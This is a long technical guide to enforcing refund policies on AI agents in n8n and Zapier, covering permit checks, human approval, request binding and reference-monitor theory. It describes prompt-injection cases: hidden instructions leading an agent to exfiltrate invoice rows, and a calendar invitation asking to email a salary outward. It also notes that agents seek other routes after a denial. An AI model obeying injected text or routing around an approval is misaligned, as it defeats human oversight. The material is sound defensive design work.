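The gateway is also one more service that can fail. If it is unavailable 0.1% of the time, the shop can't issue refunds for about 43 minutes in a 30-day month, on top of any outages at n8n or the provider. Unchecked refunds still can't go through during a gateway outage, because no request carries the provider's key without the gateway. A wrong setting can also block requests. According to AWS, an AgentCore gateway that lacks permission to evaluate the policy denies all tool calls, even those that a rule permits.

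A lost reply is more dangerous than an outage, because the workflow may record an error and repeat a refund that the provider has already paid. Agentic AI Foundation's *Deploying MCP 2026-07-28 Servers on AWS* notes that the July 2026 revision of MCP doesn't make such repeated actions safe. Its example system stores each result and returns it if the request is repeated. The refund tool needs a similar safeguard, such as paying each claim number only once.

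The gateway also can't determine why the workflow made a request. It receives the same order number, 10482, and the same amount, $80, whether the customer returned all four glasses or asked for $20 because one was broken. Surapani and colleagues separate two questions that a decision about a tool call should answer together: who passed on the authority to act, and where the content behind the action came from. The gateway can identify the workflow from its key, but an ordinary refund request contains no record of the email that led to it.

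Oracle's *The Problem with Trusting the Model* describes a prototype that supplies some of this missing information. The prototype records and locks the user's original request, then compares each action with it before applying the company's policy. If a user asks for a sales report and the agent tries to delete the file, the prototype blocks the deletion. The storage service would have allowed it because the user has permission to delete the file. Oracle gives no test results.

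This comparison needs a trusted user to state the task, and the refund mailbox has no such user. The shop would do better to have the workflow send a claim number with each refund, so the gateway can look up the damage the support team recorded.

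## When the answer is to ask a person

The shop's policy requires a person to approve the $240 refund for the lamp. The workflow normally finishes within seconds, but the approver may be at lunch or away until Monday. The workflow therefore has to pause partway and save everything it needs to continue later.

### Pausing a run

OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review*, a guide for programmers, describes the usual sequence. When an agent tries to use a tool that needs approval, the software records an interruption instead of running the tool, and saves the state of the run. In the lamp example, that state would include the customer's email, the order number and the proposed $240. After someone approves or rejects the call, the software resumes the same run from the saved state.

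The approver may never answer. In Workato, another automation product, each approval task expires after a time limit, according to its *Business approvals* instructions. Zapier's Request Approval step, which is for fixed workflows, lets the workflow's builder choose what happens at the deadline. "End run" stops the workflow. "Skip and continue" lets it carry on without a response, so the shop would pay for the lamp without anyone's approval.

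A second Zapier setting lets the run continue after the reviewer declines, which is useful for sending the customer a refusal. The payment step then needs a filter that lets it run only if the `Decision` field is `approved`. OpenAI advises programmers who build cybersecurity agents to block the action when a review times out, and the same advice suits payments.

The facts can also change during the wait. A colleague might refund the lamp by hand on Friday, and the approver might then release the workflow's refund as well on Monday. After an approval, the workflow should fetch the order record again and repeat the permit check, as McGuinness's draft requires.

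Restarting an expired request carries a similar risk. Zapier doesn't automatically replay a run that stopped because a reviewer declined or didn't respond in time. Someone has to replay the whole run, and the reviewers have to repeat every approval in it. If the workflow made a payment before the step that expired, the replay could make that payment again.

### What the approver has to see

To judge the lamp refund, an approver needs to know the action (a refund), its arguments (the amount, the order and the card) and where the request came from (the customer's email). The approver also needs the shop's own record of whether the lamp came back.

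According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in current products show a raw command on a single line, and some ask only whether to allow the action.

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) measures how much the contents of a prompt matter. In its main example, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. Hidden instructions lead the agent to copy raw invoice rows into a file, which it then asks to send to the auditor. The tool, recipient and file name all look fine, so an approver can detect the problem only by knowing what the user asked for and how the agent made the file.

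The researchers divided 80 volunteers among four versions of the approval prompt. Each person decided on twelve requests, half of them harmful, for 960 decisions in total.

| What the prompt showed | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's restriction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
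| The same facts, with the combined effect in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from adding information. The benefit of the final statement is uncertain, because after adjustment it did 7.9 percentage points better than the log, with an interval from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse. Half the requests the volunteers saw were harmful, which probably kept them more alert than someone who sees one bad refund request a month. Even so, people using the best prompt approved almost a quarter of the harmful requests.

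For the lamp refund, a useful statement might be "This refunds the full $240 to the original card. The warehouse has not recorded a return." The workflow should build this statement from data in the order system, not from the model's description.

### The approved refund must be the one that is paid

As with a permit check, a later model step could rewrite the amount before the payment. The payment step can prevent this by using the saved state. Security engineers use the term "request binding" for the general requirement that a permit be tied to the exact content of the request.

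Zapier's Request Approval step makes it easy to ignore a reviewer's correction by mistake. If the builder lets reviewers edit the content, Zapier puts their changes in new fields whose names begin with "Edited Content" and leaves the original fields unchanged. Suppose the model proposes an $80 refund for the broken glass and the reviewer corrects it to $20. If the payment step still uses the original field, the customer gets $80, and the log shows that a person reviewed the refund.

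### Approval settings in Zapier and n8n

Zapier also lets a builder require approval for a single tool in an AI step. The setting, "Require approval before running", is off by default. When it is on, the run pauses before every use of that tool, regardless of the prompt, and Zapier emails a link to the review page. The page first shows how many fields the model filled in, but the reviewer has to click the tool's name to see the values, so someone in a hurry can approve a refund without seeing the amount.

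This is much stronger than the method for the older Zapier Agents. Zapier's *Add approval steps to your agent's instructions* has the builder write a sentence telling the agent to ask for confirmation before continuing. Oracle's *Add the Human Approval Tool to the AI Agent* similarly puts a threshold in the agent's written guidelines, which require a manager's approval for expenses over $50. In both cases, the pause happens only if the model follows the instruction.

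An AI step in Zapier also pauses automatically when it reaches 75 tasks in one run (Zapier measures usage in tasks). The builder can raise the limit to 500. Akkawi (2026), in *How to build safe and trustworthy AI agents with Zapier*, describes the pause as a chance to check that the activity was expected. Like Keel's limit on model calls, the pause can stop an agent that is stuck in a loop but not a single bad refund.

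In n8n, the builder adds a human review step and connects it to the tools that need approval. According to n8n's *Human-in-the-loop for tools*, the workflow then pauses before each call to one of them and sends a request through a channel such as Slack, Teams or email. The builder writes the message and can insert the tool's name and the model's proposed parameters. The tool's name is whatever the builder called the node, so `refund_order` will help the approver more than `HTTP Request1`. If the person approves, n8n runs the tool with the model's input.

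Rejecting a call in a Zapier AI step stops the run, whereas n8n cancels the call, tells the agent and lets it continue, so the agent can explain the refusal to the customer. But *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, notes that agents look for another route after a denial. If the n8n agent has a second payment tool without a review step, it may try that one.

Both settings apply to the whole tool, but the shop wants a person to see only refunds above $100. The builder could give the agent two tools, `refund_small` without review and `refund_large` with it. Each would start a sub-workflow that runs the permit check, and the one behind `refund_small` would refuse any refund that brings the order's total refunds above $100. The model might choose the wrong tool, but that mistake wouldn't let it bypass the approver.

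### Approvals that become standing rules

Zapier takes another approach in SDK Permissions, an experimental feature for programmers whose code or AI agent uses their Zapier connections. Each login starts with an empty list of allow and deny rules. When the code makes a request that no rule covers, Zapier asks the user to approve or deny it and saves the answer as a rule. Zapier then allows or blocks similar requests without asking again.

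If the user is at the keyboard, the code can wait while the approval page opens in a browser. On a server, the code stops with an error that contains a link to the page. The programmer has to pass that link to a person and run the request again later.

A standing approval rule saves a lot of clicking, but the user approves more than the request on the screen. The rule typically covers either reading alone or both reading and writing. A user who grants write access to approve an $80 refund may also have approved the $560 refund that follows. By comparison, Mistral's agent guide, *Safety and approvals*, describes an "Always allow" option that lasts for one session.

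Zapier says SDK Permissions is "not an admin-level access-control system". Users can limit their own logins but not their colleagues'. Code that logs in by a different method bypasses the rules, and calls to Zapier's own data tables don't need approval yet. The feature can protect a careful programmer from an agent's unwanted actions, but the shop's manager couldn't use it to enforce the refund policy.

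### When builders approve their own workflows

Dana from the support team built the refund workflow, and she may also receive its approval requests. On Zapier's Pro plan, she would have to, because users can send requests from the Request Approval step only to themselves.

Her review is still useful because she knows the customers and may notice that the model has written 80 instead of 20. But many companies also want to separate duties, so that nobody can both start and approve a payment. Suppose Dana buys a lamp from the shop, keeps it, and emails the support mailbox to ask for her $240 back. The cards match, the amount is within the limit for approval, and the request arrives in her own inbox.

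Adding the finance manager as a second reviewer doesn't solve this in Zapier, because only one of the listed people can complete a review, and Dana could answer first. The policy has to choose the approver and exclude her:

1. The decision service returns `false` with an `access_request` object for the $240 refund.
2. The workflow looks up who may approve a refund of that size, for instance with Permit.io's Get Authorized Users operation.
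3. It leaves out Dana and sends the request to one of the others. n8n can send it to a specific person in Slack, and Zapier's Team and Enterprise plans let the builder name other reviewers.
4. The approver logs in to the approval service, which reports the answer to the decision service.
5. The workflow submits the refund again. The decision service returns `true` only if the approver is authorized and is not the builder.

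Dana can edit the second and third steps, so the fifth step has to enforce the rule. The approval also has to reach the decision service from the approver's own login, because if the workflow supplied an `approved_by` field, Dana could type the finance manager's name into it.

Zapier requires the builder to share the workflow with its reviewers. Before sharing it, the shop should check whether reviewers would also be able to edit it, since a reviewer who can change the payment step has the same conflict as Dana.

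### How carefully people read repeated prompts

Most of the evidence comes from coding agents, which ask programmers for permission to run commands. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of those commands are probably safe, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. A better test is to include dangerous commands and count how many people reject them.

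Hyrax reports the results of such a test in a commentary on Anthropic's announcement. People caught 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands, or 13.6%. They blocked about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic used these results to justify replacing manual review with its own classifier, so an independent replication would be valuable, but the decline within a session is hard to dismiss.

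Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this decline approval fatigue. The practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?* also said they clicked through familiar prompts and sometimes skipped the review under time pressure. Some people switch the prompts off altogether. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that user review contributed to 105 of 290 reports about agents and files. In 80 of those, users had set the agent to approve everything automatically, and in 31 the prompts were uninformative (some reports fell into both groups).

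In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) studied 113 people closer to Dana, none of whom worked in software. They supervised an agent through 18 actions in a simulated day. Seven of the actions went beyond the assigned task, such as reading bank transactions or buying a $25 lounge pass. Participants who had to approve every action allowed 40% of these overreaching actions. They spent an average of 142 seconds on all 18 actions, about 8 seconds each.

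A second group first set standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action. They saw fewer prompts, 10.9 on average, but approved 67% of the out-of-task actions they were asked about. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so most of the rules still left the decision to a prompt. Yan can't say exactly why this group approved more, and a reasonable person might welcome some of the out-of-task actions. But the result is evidence against assuming that people read each prompt more carefully when they see fewer.

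Akkawi and n8n advise starting with close review and reducing it as confidence grows. A month of approvals is weak grounds for confidence if the approver has stopped reading the requests. The shop could check this by occasionally inserting a test refund that the approver should reject, with the payment disabled.

### Two hours of approvals a day

Suppose the workflow handles 200 refunds a day and an approver spends 40 seconds on each, about the median time Hossain and colleagues measured for a prompt with a full log. Reviewing them all takes about 2.2 hours. At the 8 seconds per action in Yan's study, it would take 27 minutes. An approver who finishes that quickly is probably not opening the order records.

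Asking a person to approve only refunds above a set amount reduces the number they have to review. In this invented example, 120 refunds are for up to $50 and average $30, 50 are for $50 to $100 and average $75, 24 are for $100 to $250 and average $150, and 6 are larger.

| A person sees refunds above | Approvals a day | Time | Refunds nobody sees | Their total value |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| $0 | 200 | 2 h 13 min | 0 | $0 |
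| $50 | 80 | 53 min | 120 | $3,600 |
| $100 | 30 | 20 min | 170 | $7,350 |
| $250 | 6 | 4 min | 194 | $10,950 |

With the shop's limit of $100, the approver saves almost two hours, and $7,350 a day is refunded with no check beyond the rules. If 2% of that money is refunded wrongly, the shop loses $147 a day. Reviewing those 170 refunds as well would cost about $57 in wages at $30 an hour, so it saves money only if the approver catches more than about 39% of that loss. The volunteers who saw a full log stopped 67.5% of harmful requests, which would be enough, but the people in Anthropic's test stopped only 13.6%. The extra prompts might also make the approver less careful with the large refunds.

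An attacker who learns the limit will ask for $99, so errors below the limit may not stay small or random. The shop can also send a random 5% of these smaller refunds to a person, which adds eight or nine approvals a day, or about six minutes of work. If someone requests ten fraudulent refunds of $99 on different orders, there is a 40% chance that at least one reaches an approver, who still has to recognize it as fraud.

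## What a permit check can and cannot guarantee

Neither a careful approver nor the shop's rules can stop a refund that never reaches them. Before relying on either, the shop needs to know exactly what a working permit check guarantees about the money leaving its account.

### The guarantee as a formula

At best, every external action of a named kind has an earlier "allow" for the same request, which was still valid and which no other action had used. If *K* is the set of all actions of that kind, and *p(a)* is the permit that belongs to action *a*, the guarantee is:

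```
For every action a in K there is a permit p(a) such that

    decision(p(a)) = allow
    request(p(a))  = request(a)
    issued(p(a))   < time(a) < end(p(a))

and p(a) ≠ p(b) for every other action b in K.
```

For the shop, *K* could be every refund paid from its account at the payment provider. The definition should name an effect in the outside world, regardless of how it is triggered. If *K* covered only refunds that pass through a gateway, the guarantee would hold even while a colleague's second workflow paid customers directly. If staff also issue refunds by hand on the provider's website, the shop has to require permits for those too or limit *K* to refunds issued by software.

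The `decision` line excludes refunds that went ahead because no answer arrived, so Copilot Studio's default of running a tool when the reply is late breaks the guarantee. The `request` line requires the permit to match the refund's order, amount, currency and card. `end` is the moment when the permit expires or someone revokes it, whichever comes first, and the comparison with `issued` rules out approvals that arrive after the payment. The last line requires a separate permit for each refund, because otherwise one permit for $80 could cover seven refunds of $80.

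A shop that never pays a refund satisfies the formula, and so does a shop whose policy allows absurd refunds.

### Always invoked, tamper-proof, small enough to verify

*Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) set out the conditions for such a guarantee. It was written for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. The main danger was that a malicious user who could write programs might change the operating system and switch off its controls. Anderson's solution became known as the reference monitor, a component that checks programs' attempts to reach protected data. It must check every attempt, be tamper-proof, and be small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

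The formula holds "for every action" only if the check always runs. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) presents this as a general design principle called complete mediation, which requires a system to check every access to every object. The paper also warns against reusing the result of an earlier check, because the permission may have changed since. The time limit in the formula deals with the same problem.

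Resistance to tampering matters because anyone who can edit the check, or the facts it uses, can get any action allowed. A citizen developer usually means no harm, but she is in much the same position as Anderson's malicious user because she can program the system that contains the control. An If step in n8n therefore fails this condition whenever anyone the policy is meant to restrict can edit the workflow.

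Confidence in a permit check depends partly on the size of the mechanism, including everything it relies on. An If step is small, but trusting it means trusting n8n itself and everyone with editing rights. A gateway with two short rules also depends on the software that evaluates them, where it stores the provider's key, and the settings that control who can change either.

Tests can find flaws in a permit check, but they can't prove that none remain. The Air Force used "tiger teams", groups of experts who tried to break into its systems. Anderson noted that every known team had succeeded, but that a failed attempt would have proved little, since the team might have missed flaws. Likewise, the shop's test with one permitted and one forbidden refund can reveal a wrong connection, but it can't rule out a second payment path.

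Anderson also thought that security added to a finished system was unlikely to work. A permit check added to an existing n8n workflow is security of this kind. A gateway avoids part of the problem because it keeps the payment key out of n8n instead of trying to make n8n secure.

A clean log isn't enough either. Even if every refund in a month has a matching permit, the guarantee also depends on what else the shop's logins would have allowed. Zhou and Zhang require the approved policy to allow every effect that the credentials and enforcement rules allow. In their example, a user permits an assistant to send one summary to Alice. The system records this correctly but then issues a credential for sending mail in general. The mail service checks the credential correctly, but it would also deliver the summary to Bob, so the system fails the requirement even if no one has written to him.

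The same comparison can fail when a tool changes. If the program behind `refund_order` starts sending order data to an outside analytics company, the tool's name and arguments stay the same, and so do the permits. Zhou and Zhang propose "effect contracts", which list the data each tool may access or send and the changes it may make. Someone has to keep these lists accurate, because the check misses any effect they leave out.

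### What a monitor can and can't enforce

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Fred Schneider asked which policies a monitor can enforce if it only watches a program's steps and stops the program when necessary. Because such a monitor must work from the steps so far, it can enforce a policy only if every violation occurs at a definite point, can be identified from the steps up to that point, and cannot be corrected by any later step. Computer scientists call these policies safety properties, which require that some bad event never happens.

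The permit guarantee is a safety property. The enforcement point can identify a refund that lacks a valid permit and stop it before it goes out. To enforce the last line of the formula, the enforcement point must also remember which permits it has already used.

A permit check cannot enforce the policy "every customer who is owed a refund eventually gets one." However long a customer has waited, the refund could still arrive tomorrow, so the monitor can never determine that the policy has failed. With a ten-day deadline, the monitor could detect a failure on day ten, but stopping the workflow then wouldn't pay the customer. The shop needs a separate process that looks for unpaid claims.

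Schneider's result also explains why secrets are hard to protect with a monitor. A confidential record influenced an email if the email would have been different without it. Checking this requires comparing two possible runs, but the monitor observes only one. FORGE, the monitor that traces the origin of each argument, enforces a stricter rule that it can test within a single run. It blocks the email if the record *may* have influenced it, which is one reason it also blocks harmless work.

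A monitor can enforce a safety property only at a point where it can observe the relevant steps and stop them. For example, a limit on the total refunded per order is a safety property, but a check that has access only to the current email can't enforce it.

### Between the check and the payment

Suppose the decision service allows an $80 refund at 9:14 and the payment step runs at 9:20. In those six minutes, another step might change the amount to $800, a colleague might refund the order by hand, or the manager might suspend the workflow. Security engineers call this the gap between time of check and time of use.

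Request binding protects against a change to the refund amount after approval. The decision service stores a fingerprint of the approved request in the permit, and the enforcement point computes the request's fingerprint again immediately before the payment. If the two fingerprints differ, the enforcement point stops the refund.

The same request can look different in two programs, for instance because one puts the amount first and the other puts it last. Both programs therefore need to convert it to a standard form, called the canonical request. A common method sorts the field names alphabetically and removes unnecessary spaces:

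```json
{"amount":80,"card":"card_71","currency":"USD","order":"10482"}
```

A program then applies SHA-256, a public function that turns text of any length into a 256-bit number called a hash. Changing 80 to 800 produces a different hash, and nobody has yet found two texts with the same hash. Changing the number 80 to the text "80" also changes the hash, so an accidental conversion in an n8n step could block a legitimate refund.

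Binding doesn't help with the colleague's refund, because that refund leaves the workflow's request unchanged. Either the enforcement point has to fetch the order record again, as it does after waiting for an approver, or the order system has to reserve the amount when the service grants the permit. Zhou and Zhang point out that, with a reservation, the system must check the remaining amount and reserve the refund in one indivisible step.

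If the manager suspends the workflow, the enforcement point has to receive notice before it makes the payment. An expiry time limits the damage from missed messages, but the right length is hard to choose. Surapani and colleagues note that expiry depends on elapsed time, not on what happens in the task. A permit may still have five minutes left when the customer writes to say she has found the missing glass and no longer wants the money.

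Revoking a permit doesn't cancel a request that has already been sent. If the provider's reply never arrives, Zhou and Zhang recommend recording the outcome as unknown and counting the amount as possibly spent until the provider clarifies what happened. Even a provider that recognizes repeated requests might pay twice, because an agent could respond to the missing reply by splitting the $80 refund into two $40 refunds, which would look new to the provider. Under request binding, each of these refunds needs its own permit, and the check should deny both if the original $80 is still unresolved.

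### Keel's permit draft at the IETF

Keel, whose product for controlling model calls already uses the word "permit", has proposed a public format for permits with request binding. Munoz (2026), who works for Keel, published the first version in May as *A SCITT Profile for Pre-Execution AI Action Authorization Records*, and a revised version followed in July. SCITT is an Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) framework for signed records. The IETF publishes many of the internet's technical standards, but the permit format is only an individual draft, which anyone may submit. The July version expires in January 2027 unless a new one replaces it.

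The example permit in both versions concerns a call to a language model, but the format also covers tools and other services. For the $80 refund, it would work like this:

1. The decision service records its answer, which can be "allow", "deny" or "challenge", together with the subject, the action and the version of the policy.
2. It converts the request to canonical form and adds its SHA-256 hash to the permit.
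3. It signs the permit.
4. The enforcement point sends the request to the payment provider.
5. The service signs a second document, the closure record, with hashes of the request that went out, the provider's reply and the reply passed on to the workflow.

Keel's software also links its log entries in a chain. Each entry's hash depends on the previous entry's hash, so removing an old entry breaks the chain.

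Keel's method removes passwords and keys from the canonical request before hashing it, because an attacker with the log could otherwise use the hashes to test guesses. It also removes details that change between attempts, such as timestamps and retry identifiers. The hash therefore stays the same when a program retries a request, but a second refund of $80 on the same order would also produce that hash. To ensure that a permit is used only once, the enforcement point has to mark it as used.

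Munoz (2026) explains in *Signed Authorization-Evidence Records for WIMSE-Authorized AI Agent Actions* that the hash also covers only the body of the web request, not the address, method or headers. If a payment provider expects the order number in the web address and only the amount in the body, a permit for $80 on order 10482 would also match $80 on any other order. Munoz suggests an optional signature over the whole request, but Keel's software did not yet support this in May. Until it does, the shop could copy the order number and the address into the body before computing the hash.

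Hashes can reveal information too. Someone who obtains a permit and knows the order and the card could find the refund amount by hashing every amount from one cent to $500 until one matches. A computer can try all 50,000 almost instantly. Munoz recommends adding a secret value to the hash calculation if this matters.

### What Keel's records prove

The May version requires auditors to compare the hash in the permit with the hash of the dispatched request in the closure record. It makes the strong claim that a difference means someone changed the request after approval.

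According to the July version, the software in Keel's reference implementation copies the second hash from the permit instead of calculating it from the request it sent. If a fault had let $800 go out under an $80 permit, the two records would still match.

When a request goes through Keel's own proxy, the proxy compares it with the permit before sending it, and refuses to send it if they differ. This check may work perfectly, but it leaves no separate signed evidence. Munoz acknowledges that an auditor who has only the two records can't confirm that the request sent was the one authorized. The introduction to the July version still contains the claim that any third party can detect a change.

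Valid signatures on the records still prove that someone with Keel's signing key recorded an "allow" for a request with this hash, under a particular version of the policy. An outsider without the key can't replace either record unnoticed. Keel also has outside services timestamp its log at intervals, which makes it harder to rewrite old entries.

The permit is also more useful with independent evidence. If the payment provider's statement shows a refund of $800, the auditor can reconstruct that request, compute its hash and show that it differs from the hash in the permit. Recalculating the second hash at dispatch would improve the closure record, but that hash would still come from Keel's own software. A signed receipt from the provider would be better evidence.

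Unrecorded actions are a larger problem. Munoz states that an auditor can't detect them by examining the log alone. Even a chain that can show someone removed an entry can't reveal a refund that was never logged. To find such a refund, the auditor has to compare the log with an outside source, such as the provider's own log.

Keel's software creates closure records on a best-effort basis, so some recorded permits stay open without a warning even though the request went out. It is therefore impossible to tell from an open permit alone whether a refund happened.

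When a program sends the request itself instead of using Keel's proxy, the closure information depends on what the program reports. Keel marks the record as unverified unless the program returns a signed one. The July version states these limits openly and adds that the reference implementation doesn't yet produce the type of signature the draft requires.

### Comparing the three placements

A company can run the permit check as a step in the workflow, as a call by the platform, or at a gateway. It can compare these options in four ways, based on the conditions for the guarantee.

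| Placement | Who can remove the check | Which actions it sees | What happens on failure | Is the request bound? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Step in the workflow | Anyone who can edit the workflow | Actions on its own path, and an agent's tool calls only if the check is inside the tool | Depends on the builder's error settings | Only if the payment step uses the checked values |
| Platform check in Copilot Studio | The platform's administrators | Tool calls by generative agents in that environment | The tool runs by default, but administrators can choose to block it | The platform should run the call it described, but outsiders can't confirm this |
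| Gateway that holds the payment key | The gateway's administrators | Requests that need this key | If the gateway is down, no payment goes out. If only the decision service is down, the gateway's settings apply | Yes, if the gateway forwards exactly what it checked |

The gateway comes closest to the formula, provided that no other copy of the key works, but it has little information about the reason for a request. Surapani and colleagues describe this as a general trade-off. Moving a check away from the model and closer to the outside service gives it more control over the action but less information about the task.

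In one constructed example, a user asks a calendar assistant to summarize the week's meetings, and one invitation contains a request to send the user's salary to an outside address. A check beside the model can block the email, but it may miss the problem without a record of where the text came from, and it has no effect on a call that takes another route. A gateway in front of the mail service can detect only that a valid program is trying to email an outsider, so it has to block all such emails or let this one through. A check in the software that runs the agent can trace the request to the invitation, but it can't stop an email that bypasses this software. The example is not an experiment, but these limits follow from the information each component receives.

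The shop can split the work between the agent platform and the gateway. A check inside the platform, where the email and earlier steps are available, issues a permit for one exact refund. The gateway then hashes the request it is about to forward, compares the hash with the permit, marks the permit as used and adds the payment key. Request binding makes this split safe because nobody can edit the refund between the two points. The first check must still take its facts from the order system, because the gateway will enforce the decision even if it is wrong.

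### What 90% coverage means

Suppose employees, customers and misled agents attempt 100 prohibited refunds in a month. If 90 of them reach a perfect permit check, it stops those 90, but the other 10 still happen. Better rules can't prevent those 10 because they never reach the check.

Let *c* be the share of prohibited refunds that reach the check, and *d* the share of those that it stops. The share that still happens is 1 − *c* × *d*. Out of 100 prohibited refunds, the shop would pay:

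| Reach the check | Check stops 80% | Check stops 90% | Check stops 100% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | 60 | 55 | 50 |
| 90% | 28 | 19 | 10 |
| 99% | 21 | 11 | 1 |

Suppose a shop's permit check covers 90% of prohibited refund attempts and stops 90% of those it covers. The shop still pays 19 of every 100 prohibited refunds. A perfect check would reduce this to 10, and extending coverage to 99% would reduce it to about 11, so the shop should choose whichever improvement is cheaper. At 50% coverage, even a perfect check would let half of the prohibited refunds through, so the shop should first look for the unchecked paths.

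The calculation depends on the share of *prohibited* refunds that go through the check, which is harder to measure than the share of all refunds. Suppose the shop processes 10,000 refunds a month, 100 of which are prohibited, and the check covers 9,900 of the 10,000, or 99%. If 60 of the prohibited refunds are among the 100 that skip the check, even a perfect check stops only 40. Prohibited refunds are quite likely to skip the check when people cheat on purpose, because an employee who wants to pay herself will choose the unchecked path.

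Average coverage is a reasonable guide to protection against honest mistakes, such as a model writing 80 instead of 20, because the model doesn't choose its route to avoid the check. Coverage is effectively zero against an attacker who knows of an unchecked path. Anderson's panel described computer security as a question of completeness and not of degree, which is about right for a determined attacker. The shop can still benefit from 90% coverage if most of its losses come from mistakes.

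A second check helps only with the refunds that the first one misses. Suppose a platform check misses 10% of prohibited refunds and a gateway check misses 5%. If the misses are independent, 0.5% of prohibited refunds get past both checks. If the platform check also misses every refund that the gateway check misses, 5% do. The higher figure is often more realistic, because a workflow that an employee builds in another tool with a personal login avoids both checks.

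### Problems that remain with any placement

Even with full coverage and perfect request binding, the shop could pay $80 for one broken glass, because the rules allow it. The permit would match the payment, and every line of the formula would hold. The guarantee covers only enforcement of the policy. Zhou and Zhang emphasize that writing a correct policy is a separate task.

An attacker can also stay within the limits. If the shop has 200 orders a day and allows refunds of up to $100 on each without a person's approval, the check could permit $20,000 a day in undeserved refunds. The guarantee is still valuable because it turns an unlimited loss into one that the shop can calculate and reduce, for instance with a daily cap. But someone has to calculate the possible loss for the whole account, since a small limit per order may add up to a large total.

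Permitted actions can also reveal more together than separately. An agent allowed to read delivery addresses, delivery dates and customers' emails might work out who is away from home next week, even though no single record contains that information. Surapani and colleagues reviewed the literature and found no mechanism that limits such combined use of information to what the original task requires. They consider this the least developed part of agent authorization.

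Surapani and colleagues distinguish proof that someone's key signed an approval from proof that the person understood and intended its effect. The finance manager's signed approval for the $240 lamp shows that someone used her login, but not that she noticed the missing warehouse record.

Finally, a permit doesn't prove that the refund happened. The provider might reject the refund because the shop's balance is too low, or the customer's bank might return it two days after the provider accepts it. A closure record can contain a hash of the provider's first reply, but that reply may have been only "accepted for processing". To know whether the customer has her money, the shop has to check the refund's final status with the provider.

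## How workflows escape the check, and the settings that prevent it

A refund can skip the check only if someone was allowed to build a way around it. Dana may edit her workflow, add a step that contacts any web address, and store her own login. She may also be able to install a component from the internet or open an account with another automation tool. An administrator can limit most of these rights with a setting, though each has ordinary uses.

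### Editing the workflow

When the check is a step in the workflow, anyone with editing rights can leave it out, delete it or bypass it by connecting an earlier step directly to the payment. NeuralTrust tells customers that its check has no effect on workflows that omit it.

n8n sorts workflows and credentials into projects, and each member of a project has a role. A Viewer can read everything in the project but can't run or change it. An Editor can add, change and run workflows, and an Admin can also manage the members, according to n8n. The Viewer role would stop Dana from removing the check, but it would also stop her from maintaining her own workflow.

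Custom roles are a middle option. n8n has separate permissions for creating and publishing workflows, so Dana could build a workflow and someone in finance could publish it. n8n's *Set permissions and roles (RBAC)* says that custom roles require an Enterprise plan.

Removing someone's right to publish doesn't stop them from doing test runs, however. A manual run with the live payment key makes real payments, so a draft without a check could issue a refund before anyone reviews it. n8n's *Changelog* describes a change in version 2.46, from October 2026, that reduces this risk. Each workflow now runs under one person's account and can use only the credentials that person may use. If the finance manager adds her personal payment login to the team's workflow without sharing it, Dana can edit the workflow but can't run or publish it with that login. This is stricter than the sharing rule described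 earlier, which let anyone who could edit a shared workflow use every credential in it. However, the manager now has to publish each of Dana's edits.

The roles need protection too. n8n warns that a user allowed to manage project roles can add permissions to their own role, and that a user allowed to manage members can invite a second account they control and make it an administrator.

### Review before publication, and parts the builder can't open

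A review works best when the builder's copy has no access to the live payment key. n8n 3.1, released in November 2026, supports this with a new version of its Environments feature, which moves selected workflows from one n8n installation to another. Dana would work on a development installation with a test key from the payment provider. An administrator would then review each change on a diagram of the workflow and apply it to the live installation. Only owners and administrators of an installation can promote, review or apply changes. The transfer doesn't include the secret part of any credential, so the live key can stay on the live installation. The feature is for Enterprise customers, and n8n still labels it a preview.

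The reviewer should look for a new payment, HTTP or code step, a changed credential, and any path to the payment that skips the check. Most edits will contain none of these. Reviewers can tire of harmless edits just as approvers tire of harmless refunds, so it helps to keep the dangerous part out of workflows that people edit often.

The permit check and the payment have to stay together in one sub-workflow that builders can call but not open. If builders copied them from a template instead, they could remove the check from their copies. In n8n, the IT department could keep the `refund_order` sub-workflow in a separate project where Dana has no role. Her workflow would send it an order number and an amount, and she could still change anything in her own workflow.

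n8n's newer agents, also in preview, can likewise call a workflow that runs with its own credentials. In n8n's example, an agent adds a note to a customer database without having write access to the database. For an ordinary workflow, IT should test whether Dana's run can call a sub-workflow that contains a credential she may not use, because version 2.46 ties each run to one person's credentials.

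### General web requests and custom code

Blocking the payment provider's connector achieves little if a builder has a valid key and can send the same refund request through a general HTTP step. n8n has three ways to block step types.

| Control | What it does | Who can use it | Main limit |
|---|---|---|---|
| `NODES_EXCLUDE` | Stops n8n from loading the listed steps | Whoever runs a self-hosted server | Applies to every project and needs a restart |
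| Node type policies (October 2026) | Block steps for a whole installation or one project | Enterprise administrators, through n8n's programming interface | Project administrators can switch on some blocked steps |
| Node and credential policies (November 2026) | Restrict types of step and types of credential from a settings page | Enterprise customers | A preview that n8n advises against relying on in production |

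n8n's *Block specific nodes* recommends the first for steps that must never run. The exclusion list isn't empty to begin with. By default it contains Execute Command, which runs commands on the server, and a trigger that watches local files. An administrator who writes a new list replaces the old one, so the new list has to repeat these two entries. n8n's own example repeats Execute Command but leaves out the file trigger, which would therefore become available.

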